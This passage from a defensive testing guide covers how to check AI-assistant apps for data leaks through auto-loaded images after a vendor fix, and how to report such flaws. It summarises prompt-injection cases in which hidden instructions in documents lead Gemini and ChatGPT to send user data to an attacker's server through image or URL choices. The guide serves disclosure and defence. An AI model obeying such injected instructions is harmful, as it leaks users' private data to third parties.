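| The client could not display that form of output | Run the control in the same form, such as an HTML image |

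#### Stored copies

Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* documentation says that Claude's page-fetching tool, like a browser, caches results, and that how it does so may change over time. A tester who asks Claude to open the same page twice may therefore see only one request.

The same documentation lists error codes that help explain silence. A developer who uses the tool through Anthropic's API gets `url_not_allowed` if a rule blocked the address and `url_not_accessible` if the fetch failed. The code `url_too_long` means the address exceeded 250 characters, so the tester can shorten it and try again. These codes cover only the tool, and a client that leaves out an image may give no reason.

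#### Blocked and late requests

Before a device requests an image, it normally has to look up the IP address for the server's name. Some listeners record these lookups too. If a lookup arrives without a web request, the device may have tried to connect and failed, perhaps because of a firewall. The lookup is poor evidence of who made it, because it often arrives through another company's server. In *How can I be sure about "External service interaction (DNS)" issue*, Marc (2021) asked about a lookup that seemed to come from Google, and an employee of the security company PortSwigger gave this explanation.

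Silence also means only that no request has arrived yet. In *Cracking the Lens*, Kettle (2017) used a listener to find hidden systems between users and websites. Some callbacks arrived after three minutes, others after several hours, and in one case they came every 24 hours. An image in a chat should load much sooner, but a late callback may reveal a server that stored the address, so the listener should keep running for a few days after the test.

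#### Rollout groups

A vendor may release a change in stages, so some users get it before others. OpenAI's *ChatGPT release notes* (2026) describe several features as rolling out gradually, often by plan or region, and state that some eligible users may not see one of these features right away. The notes are about features, but a vendor could release a security fix the same way.

A tester whose account already has the fix will get silence in every trial, even if the app still leaks for other people. Further trials on that account don't help. If half of all accounts have the fix, there is a 50% chance that a single test account has it, and a 3% chance that five randomly chosen accounts all do. If 90% have it, the tester needs 29 accounts to bring the chance that they all have it below 5%. Asking the vendor whether the rollout is complete is much easier, but the test report should then attribute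 that claim to the vendor.

Phone app updates can also be released in stages. Under the phased release described in Apple's *App Store Connect Help*, 1% of users with automatic updates get a new version on the first day, 10% on the fourth and all of them by the seventh. Apple doesn't tell these users that they are in a phased release, and the developer can pause it for up to 30 days. But anyone can download the new version manually, so a tester who updates the app before testing may be using a version that most people won't receive for days.

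Differences between a vendor's servers can have the same effect. Kettle had a 30% chance of finding one flaw at Yahoo in any single scan, because Yahoo spread requests over three servers and only one had the flaw. More trials do help here, as long as each one has a new chance of reaching the vulnerable server. Nine scans would have had about a 96% chance of finding the flaw.

### How many silent trials are enough

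The number of trials needed depends on how often an exposed client would call back. If it does so in 89% of trials, the chance of silence is 11% in one trial and about 0.1% (0.11³) in three. If the tester's instructions work less well and an exposed client calls back in only 25% of trials, three trials would all be silent 42% of the time. It would then take 11 trials to bring the chance of complete silence below 5% (0.75¹¹ ≈ 4.2%).

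If an exposed client calls back with probability *p* in each independent trial, the chance that all *n* trials are silent is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The table gives the smallest *n* that brings this chance below 5%.

| Callback rate of an exposed client | Silent trials needed | Chance of that much silence |
|---|---|---|
| 89% | 2 | 1.2% |
| 60% | 4 | 2.6% |
| 25% | 11 | 4.2% |
| 10% | 29 | 4.7% |
| 1% | 299 | just under 5% |

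The tester should measure the callback rate on a version of the client that is known to leak, if one is available. A rate from another product, or even an average for the same product, isn't a safe substitute. In *Silent Egress* the lowest rate for any combination was 60%, and at that rate a client that still leaks has a 6.4% chance of staying silent in three trials, instead of 0.1%. In *What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove*, Kaur (2026) calls for the same measurement in AI safety tests generally. AI laboratories often have a reference model that is known to show the behaviour in question, but Kaur finds that they almost never report how often their test detects it.

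A tester needs far fewer trials if they can read the raw answer and exclude every trial in which the model didn't write the address. In the remaining trials, a client without the fix should load the image almost every time, provided it can display that form. Three of these trials are better evidence than 11 in which nobody knows what the model wrote.

#### The chance that the client is still exposed

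The 4.2% in the table is the chance that an exposed client would stay silent. The chance that a silent client is exposed also depends on how likely the tester thought exposure was before the trials. Suppose the vendor has forgotten to fix its phone apps before, and the tester thinks it 90% likely that this one lacks the fix, which is odds of 9 to 1. Eleven silent trials multiply those odds by 0.042, giving 0.38 to 1, which is still a 28% chance that the app is exposed. With the 89% callback rate, three silent trials would lower the chance from 90% to about 1%. Both results assume that an app with the fix never calls back.

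Kaur's paper uses this way of updating odds to defend clean results against critics who consider them nearly worthless. In its example, 520 prompts test whether a model does something harmful 1% or 0.5% of the time. A run with no harmful answers is then 1.4 times as strong as evidence as a run with one. Silence can therefore be strong evidence if a callback was likely. But a single valid callback refutes the claim that no client ever loads such an address.

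#### When the callback rate is unknown

A tester who has no leaking version to compare with can still calculate an upper bound on the callback rate. If 30 independent trials produce no callbacks, the 95% upper bound is about 10%, because a true rate of 10% would produce 30 silent trials only 4.2% of the time, and higher rates would do so even less often. Dividing three by the number of trials approximates this bound.

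A 10% limit is uncomfortably high, because an attacker who succeeds 10% of the time has a better than even chance of succeeding at least once in seven attempts. Lowering the limit to 1% takes about 300 trials, which is practical for an automated test but hardly practical by hand on a phone. It is usually more useful to confirm what the model wrote, or to look for the policy or check that blocked the image.

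The bound also applies only to the conditions tested, so 30 silent trials with Markdown images give no bound on the callback rate for HTML images.

### Why repeating one address is not enough

These calculations require independent trials, where the result of one does not determine the result of the next. Trials that repeat the same address are not independent if the verdict depends on the address.

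Suppose a tester in December 2023 had tried `d.png` 30 times in the web app. If url_safe had returned the same result each time, all 30 trials would have been silent. The tester would have calculated an upper bound of 10% on the approval rate of a check that approved 25% of the addresses in Rehberger's test. A single address chosen at random from those 36 had a 75% chance of silence, however often the tester repeated it. Eleven different addresses chosen at random would have had about a 98% chance of including at least one of the nine that loaded.

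The web index that OpenAI now uses creates the same dependence, since a repeated address should get the same verdict until the index changes.

Statisticians call a set of related trials a cluster. Kaur's standard correction for clusters divides the number of trials by 1 + (*m* − 1) × *ρ*, where *m* is the number of trials per cluster and *ρ* (rho) measures how similar their results are, from 0 for unrelated to 1 for identical. If a tester repeats each of three addresses ten times and the verdict never varies, *ρ* is 1 and the divisor is 10. The 30 trials then count as three, and the upper bound rises from 10% to 63%. If *ρ* were 0.1, they would count as about 16. Kaur cautions that the correction is approximate when *ρ* is between 0 and 1, and recommends modeling the clusters to get exact limits.

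Using a new token in every trial removes the most obvious dependence between trials. Some dependence remains if all the addresses are on one server, because a check based on the server's name will treat them alike. Running some trials with a second listener on an unrelated domain helps reveal this. Trials on the same account are also dependent, so 30 trials on one account test only one rollout group.

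What the tester counts as a trial also matters. Kaur's example is the safety report on Anthropic's Claude 2, in which the model gave a harmful response to four of 328 prompts. Anthropic had collected five responses to each prompt but reported only the number of prompts, so readers can't work out how often a single response was harmful. By Kaur's definition, a tester who rewords an instruction 20 times until the model obeys has run one trial, because each attempt builds on the last.

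### Wording that a test report can defend

"No leaks found" and "0% callback rate" are too vague. *Limits of Statistical Assurance for Embodied and Agentic AI under Adaptive Adversaries* (2026) examines how AI developers report results of zero and points out that 0% may not mean zero events if the total and the rounding rule aren't given. A test report should give the number of trials, say what counted as a trial, and limit its conclusion to the clients and conditions tested.

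After a callback, a defensible statement about the Android app in the earlier invented example might read:

On 16 November 2026, version 5.1.3 of the Android app requested a test address that contained invented conversation data. The request came from the test phone's IP address one second after the answer appeared, and nobody had clicked anything. Ten minutes earlier, the web app had received the same address from the assistant and had not requested it. This version of the Android app either lacks the check or does not act on its result.

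For a client that stayed silent, the wording has to be more limited. If the team ran 30 further trials on the iPhone app, it could write:

Between 16 and 18 November 2026, we ran 30 trials of Markdown images in new conversations on version 5.2.0 of the iPhone app. We used three accounts, two listeners on unrelated domains and a different address for each trial. The raw answer contained the complete address every time, and neither listener recorded a request for it within ten minutes. Control images loaded before and after each trial. If the trials were independent, the 95% upper bound on the callback rate under these conditions is about 10%. This result does not cover reopened conversations, other image notations or earlier versions of the app. The vendor told us that the rollout was complete, but we could not confirm this.

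## Naming, reporting and closing an incomplete fix

A client may load a forbidden address for any of four reasons, which all look the same in the listener's log. In an incomplete rollout, the fix works in some clients, but the vendor never added it to this one. In a bypass, the fix is running in the client, but data gets out anyway. In a regression, the client had a working fix but lost it. Or the vendor may know about the behaviour and have decided to accept it.

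### Telling the findings apart

One further observation usually separates any two of these findings.

| Possible findings | Observation that separates them |
|---|---|
| Incomplete rollout or bypass | Try an ordinary address that another client has just blocked. If this client loads it, the fix is missing. If this client blocks it and leaks only through an altered address or another notation, the finding is a bypass. |
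| Incomplete rollout or regression | Look for results from older versions of the same client. If one of them blocked the address, the finding is a regression. |
| Bypass or regression | Repeat the exact attack that the fix originally stopped. If it works again, the finding is a regression. If only a changed attack works, it is a bypass. |
| Accepted behaviour or incomplete rollout | Repeat the test in a client that has the fix. If the data leaks there too, a missing fix is not the explanation. |
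| Accepted behaviour or bypass | Compare the address with the vendor's published rule, or ask the vendor. The log can't settle this. |
| Accepted behaviour or regression | Ask the vendor whether it removed the protection on purpose. |

An outside tester can't load last year's version of a website and can rarely install an old phone app. Without a dated record of what an earlier version did, the tester can't tell a regression from an incomplete rollout.

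The label determines who has to act. In an incomplete rollout, the team that builds the exposed client has to add the existing fix. The tester should also test every client that has no result of its own, since the vendor may have overlooked more than one. The people who maintain the check have to fix a bypass, and if several clients share that check, all of them need retesting. After a regression, the vendor has to find the release that removed the protection and identify which other clients received the same change. If the vendor accepts the behaviour and won't change it, the organisations that use the assistant have to decide whether they can tolerate the risk.

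Some findings fit two labels. In the invented test described earlier, the Mac app blocked Markdown images but loaded HTML images, while the web app blocked both. This is a bypass, because the Mac app's check runs but misses HTML images. It also resembles an incomplete rollout, because the web app already has code that handles HTML images, and the repair may be as simple as copying it. A report should give both observations as well as the label.

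### Google AI Studio, August 2024

Rehberger could not classify one of his findings. He had previously written about an image leak in Google AI Studio, a website where developers try out Google's Gemini models. Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio* describes what "appeared to be a regression or bypass" that let data out again. Variations on Markdown images worked only occasionally, but the attack became much simpler when he had the model write an HTML image tag. In his demonstration, a user uploads a set of employee performance reviews, one of which contains a hidden instruction. AI Studio then sends a summary of each of the other employees' reviews to his server.

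He added that the HTML leak might have existed all along, since AI Studio had no Content Security Policy. The leak was a regression if an earlier fix had covered HTML tags and an update had undone it, or a bypass if the fix had only ever covered Markdown. Testing an HTML tag just after the earlier fix would have shown which it was, but his post mentions no such test. A bypass seems more likely, because his trouble with Markdown suggests that some protection against Markdown images was still running.

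Google fixed the leak by displaying image tags as text, which it could do without knowing whether the leak was a regression or a bypass. The distinction would still have mattered to anyone who had used AI Studio since the earlier fix. A regression would have exposed them only after the update that caused it, while a bypass would have exposed them for the whole period.

### ZombieAgent, September 2025

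On 18 September 2025, the security company Radware (2025) announced ShadowLeak, an attack that made ChatGPT's Deep Research agent send private data from OpenAI's own servers. The hidden instructions typically told ChatGPT to add the data to an attacker's web address, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*, and OpenAI responded by forbidding ChatGPT to modify web addresses.

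Eight days after the announcement, Radware reported a way around the new rule. *ZombieAgent* explains that ChatGPT opened only unaltered addresses, as the rule required, but conveyed the data through its choice of addresses. This was a bypass because the rule was in force and only a changed attack worked.

The requests came from OpenAI's servers, so this attack did not depend on the client. Radware also got a weaker variant to work with Markdown images in the user's browser, and that variant needs a test in each client.

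### Two Tenable reports

The url_safe flaw that Tenable reported in December 2024 was also a bypass. ChatGPT sent addresses to url_safe, which approved every address on one domain, including those that forward visitors to other sites. The team behind url_safe had to fix the flaw, and any client that relied on the service was exposed until they did.

The other case, described in Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025), is harder to label. It involved links to ChatGPT's website that contained a prompt. The site submitted the prompt as soon as the page loaded, so one click on a link could start an attack. Tenable reported this on 15 April 2025. By 22 April OpenAI had released a fix to 1% of users, and on 30 April it told Tenable that everyone had it. On 6 May Tenable found that the problem persisted.

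Between 22 and 30 April this was an incomplete rollout within a single client, since 99% of users did not have the fix. The finding of 6 May could mean that the rollout had missed some accounts or that the fix was too weak. Tenable doesn't say what it tried that day. But two days later OpenAI asked Tenable for ideas on how to fix the flaw, which suggests that the fix was too weak. On 11 July OpenAI said it had improved url_safe and restricted automatic submission. The restriction uses a header in which the browser indicates whether a request came from another site.

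### How vendors answered

Many vendors run a bug bounty program, which pays outsiders for reporting flaws. Each report first goes through triage, where someone decides whether it is valid and how urgent it is. OpenAI uses an outside company, Bugcrowd, to triage reports.

PromptArmor reported the leak in OpenAI's log viewer on 17 November 2025. It supplied step-by-step instructions three days later and answered questions on 24, 25 and 26 November. On 4 December the report was closed as not applicable. After PromptArmor published its findings, OpenAI confirmed the flaw and reopened the report on 22 January 2026. PromptArmor says OpenAI had not seen the original report because Bugcrowd had triaged it. It concedes that prompt injection flaws are difficult to triage because they take many forms and often don't fit the existing categories.

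Bugcrowd handled the ZombieAgent report much faster. It asked for more details within two hours, reproduced the attack four days after the first report and forwarded it to OpenAI. OpenAI then took another 77 days to fix the flaw, so triage was only a small part of the delay.

Google gave Rehberger no timetable for the AI Studio leak through its official intake. He tagged Logan Kilpatrick, a product lead at Google, in a public message on X. Kilpatrick replied on 7 August 2024 that he was on it, and Google fixed the leak within 24 hours. The fix evidently took little work once the right person knew about the leak. But a public message is an unreliable substitute for triage, because a lesser-known researcher might have received no reply.

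Microsoft rejected a report from Checkmarx about Copilot Chat. Checkmarx had demonstrated an attack that used an image address to send an API key, which was no longer valid, out of a developer's working environment. Checkmarx filed the report on 15 October 2025, and on 28 October Microsoft said that its engineers were still working on the issue. On 4 November Microsoft marked the report "Completed" without a fix. In a letter that Checkmarx published, Microsoft said that the attack needed multiple user actions outside the default setup, that it "does not reliably reproduce across environments", and that the product displayed warnings. Microsoft also said it assumes that users review and trust the code they choose to run. It passed the report to the engineering team, which would look for ways to make the behaviour more transparent.

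Google declined to treat one-click leaks in Gemini as a security bug. The official status was "Infeasible", but the main reason Google gave in its letter was that the risk was not serious enough to justify the monitoring and escalation procedures a product team must follow when Google files a security bug. Checkmarx found the answer acceptable but thought users should be warned, since it leaves them to manage the risk.

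These reasons deserve some weight. An attack that works only after a user has changed settings and ignored warnings endangers fewer people than one that works by default. Checkmarx itself acknowledges that getting the agent to read the hostile page can be difficult. Since no vendor can make a model resist every prompt injection, escalating each successful one would take engineers away from the leaks they can close.

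Poor reproducibility is a weaker reason to close a report when the suspected problem is an incomplete rollout. The leak reproduces every time, but only in clients the fix hasn't reached. A triager who tries an iPhone attack in a desktop browser will see no leak and may close the report. Nothing suggests that this happened with Copilot Chat. Finders can guard against it by naming the exact client and version in the report's first sentence.

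### What bug bounty programs require

OpenAI's rules have become more explicit since the dispute over the log viewer. On 25 March 2026, OpenAI (2026) opened a Safety Bug Bounty for problems that may not count as conventional security flaws. It covers attacks in which a third party's text hijacks an agent and makes it leak the user's sensitive information, provided the attack works at least 50% of the time.

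OpenAI's announcement doesn't specify how many trials a finder needs. Five successes in five trials are good evidence that an attack works at least half the time, because an attack with a lower success rate would succeed in all five at most about 3% of the time.

The 50% rule can work against someone who reports a flaw in a client. Suppose the model writes the test address in 8 of 20 trials, and the phone app loads it all 8 times. The complete attack works only 40% of the time, but the phone app failed in every trial that tested it. The person reporting the flaw should give both figures, and can reword the test document so that the model complies more often.

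A missing client check is not on the program's list of examples, but OpenAI considers other flaws case by case if they lead directly to user harm and have a specific remedy. Adding the web app's existing check to a phone app would be a specific remedy. Finders needn't worry much about choosing between this program and OpenAI's older Security Bug Bounty, because OpenAI may move reports between them.

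Google and Microsoft stress the consequences of an attack in their letters to Checkmarx. Google's reward program covers only flaws that "substantially affect the confidentiality or integrity of user data". Microsoft rates AI flaws by their impact and how easily an attacker can exploit them. A report to either company should therefore state which data left the client, under which settings, and everything the user had to do. Writing "The user asked for a summary and clicked nothing" is more useful than writing "zero-click", because people define that term differently.

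### What to put in the report

The first sentence of a report on an incomplete fix should name the client and the missing protection. For the invented assistant, it could be: "Version 5.1.3 of the Android app loads an image from an address containing conversation data, although the web app blocks the same address." A table of all the clients can follow.

| Client and version | Test tokens | Result | Proposed label |
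|---|---|---|---|
| Web app in Firefox 150 | `m4x8`, `h7c2` | Blocked the Markdown and HTML images | Fix works |
| Android app 5.1.3 | `m4x8` | Loaded the Markdown image | Incomplete rollout, unless an earlier version blocked it |
| Mac app 3.4.0 | `m6k3`, `h7c2` | Blocked the Markdown image, loaded the HTML image | Bypass |
| iPhone app 5.2.0 | `m5r1`, `m8t6` | Blocked the Markdown image in a new chat, loaded one in a reopened chat | Bypass |
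| Windows app 3.4.0 | `m9d5`, `h3w8` | Blocked the Markdown image, loaded the HTML image in a reopened chat | Bypass |

The shared tokens show the triager that the Android and Mac apps loaded addresses that the web app had already blocked.

The rest of the report should contain:

- The earlier fix, with its date, the vendor's report number and any public description of it.
- The operating system, type of account, region and relevant settings for each client.
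- The log line and the raw answer for each token, with times in Coordinated Universal Time.
- The positive controls, including any that failed.
- The number of trials, how often the model wrote the address and how often the client then loaded it.
- The shortest steps that reproduce the result, along with the test document.
- The clients that the finder could not test.

The steps should warn the triager not to type or paste the test address into the chat. A triager who did so in ChatGPT might get a legitimate callback and dismiss the report as intended behaviour.

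A suggested repair can also help, as OpenAI's request to Tenable shows. When a fix has reached only some clients, the finder can point to the one where it already works.

Separate problems belong in separate reports that refer to each other. If the Android team fixes its app and the vendor closes the only report, the Mac app's HTML leak may be overlooked while it is still unfixed.

### When to publish

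Publishing before every client is safe can help attackers, but when a rollout is incomplete, much of the information is often already public. Once someone has described the original attack and the web app's fix, anyone can try the same attack in the phone app. Staying silent then protects users less than it would for an unknown flaw, and users won't know to switch to the protected client until the other one is fixed.

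When a bypass defeats a check that the clients share, users may have no protected client to switch to, so there is a stronger case for withholding the details until the vendor has repaired the check. Users can still benefit from a general warning, for example to disconnect their e-mail account from the assistant.

Publicity has a mixed record of getting flaws fixed. OpenAI reopened the log viewer report only after PromptArmor's article, and Google fixed AI Studio within a day of a public message. But ChatGPT's iPhone app lacked url_safe for nine months after Rehberger publicly said it was missing.

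Researchers have also chosen different moments to publish. Tenable told OpenAI that it would publish the flaw in ChatGPT's prompt links on 14 July 2025, 90 days after reporting it. OpenAI announced its improvements three days before that date. Tenable asked for news about the url_safe bypass six times between 17 December 2024 and 4 March 2025, and its timeline records only one step by OpenAI in that period, adding another person to the conversation. Tenable published while the bypass still worked. Radware waited for the fix to ZombieAgent and published 23 days later.

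Delaying publication after a fix is most useful for installed apps, because people need time to update them. Check Point published its Lockdown Mode bypass seven weeks after OpenAI fixed it, although users had nothing to install.

The finder can reasonably give the vendor a publication date in the first report, such as 90 days later. If some clients are still exposed on that date, the finder can name them, list the versions tested and tell users how to protect themselves, without including attack instructions that work on those clients. If a triager rejects the report, the finder should write to the vendor's own security team before publishing, because PromptArmor's experience suggests that the vendor may not know the report exists.

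### What closes a case

A report can be closed without a fix. Microsoft marked the Copilot Chat report "Completed", Google marked the Gemini links report "Infeasible", and the log viewer report was closed as "not applicable", but none of these closures came with a fix. Anyone who relies on a vendor's tracker should also read the reason for closure, not only the status.

For an installed app, the vendor should name the first version that contains the fix, such as version 1.2024.247 of ChatGPT's Mac app. It should also say what happens to older versions that can still connect. A website or a service on the vendor's servers may have no public version number, so the vendor has to give the date the rollout reached all users instead.

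The finder should then repeat the test. After OpenAI repaired the Lockdown Mode bypass in September 2026, Check Point retested and found that the technique no longer worked, according to Duggan, who read the company's full report. He did not check the fix himself or say whether the retest covered both the browser and the desktop app. A complete retest would have included both, since the attack had behaved differently in each.

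In other cases, only the vendor confirmed the fix. Check Point Research writes that OpenAI had already discovered the hidden path out of ChatGPT's code environment and that the fix was "fully deployed" on 20 February 2026, but mentions no retest. Radware's ZombieAgent timeline also ends with OpenAI's fix, and TechRadar's *This 'ZombieAgent' zero click vulnerability allows for silent account takeover* notes the lack of detail about how OpenAI fixed the flaw. These fixes may work, but OpenAI had also told Tenable in April 2025 that everyone had the fix for the prompt links, and Tenable still found the problem when it retested six days later.

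A finder should wait until the vendor says that the rollout is complete, and then retest on more than one account.

The retest should include the attack from the report, the older attack that the first fix stopped, and a harmless image that the client is supposed to load. If the harmless image doesn't appear either, the vendor may have broken image loading altogether, and repairing it later could bring back the leak. After a bypass, the finder should also try a few close variations of the attack, because the vendor may have blocked only the exact example in the report.

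Sometimes the finder cannot retest a fix because the vulnerable component is gone. Check Point found a channel between ChatGPT accounts that ran through an internal server for software packages. The channel was gone by the time Check Point completed its report, and OpenAI confirmed that it had shut the server down, according to eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Flaw Let Attackers Secretly Hijack a Victim’s AI Session*. Such a case can close without a fixed version number, but the vendor should say whether another server now does the same job, since the replacement could have the same flaw.

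When some clients are safe and others are not, the case should stay open with a separate status for each client. An entry for the invented assistant might read: "Android was fixed in 5.1.4, and the finder retested it on 2 December 2026. Mac and Windows are still exposed to HTML images. The iPhone fix was released in 5.2.1 but has not yet been retested."
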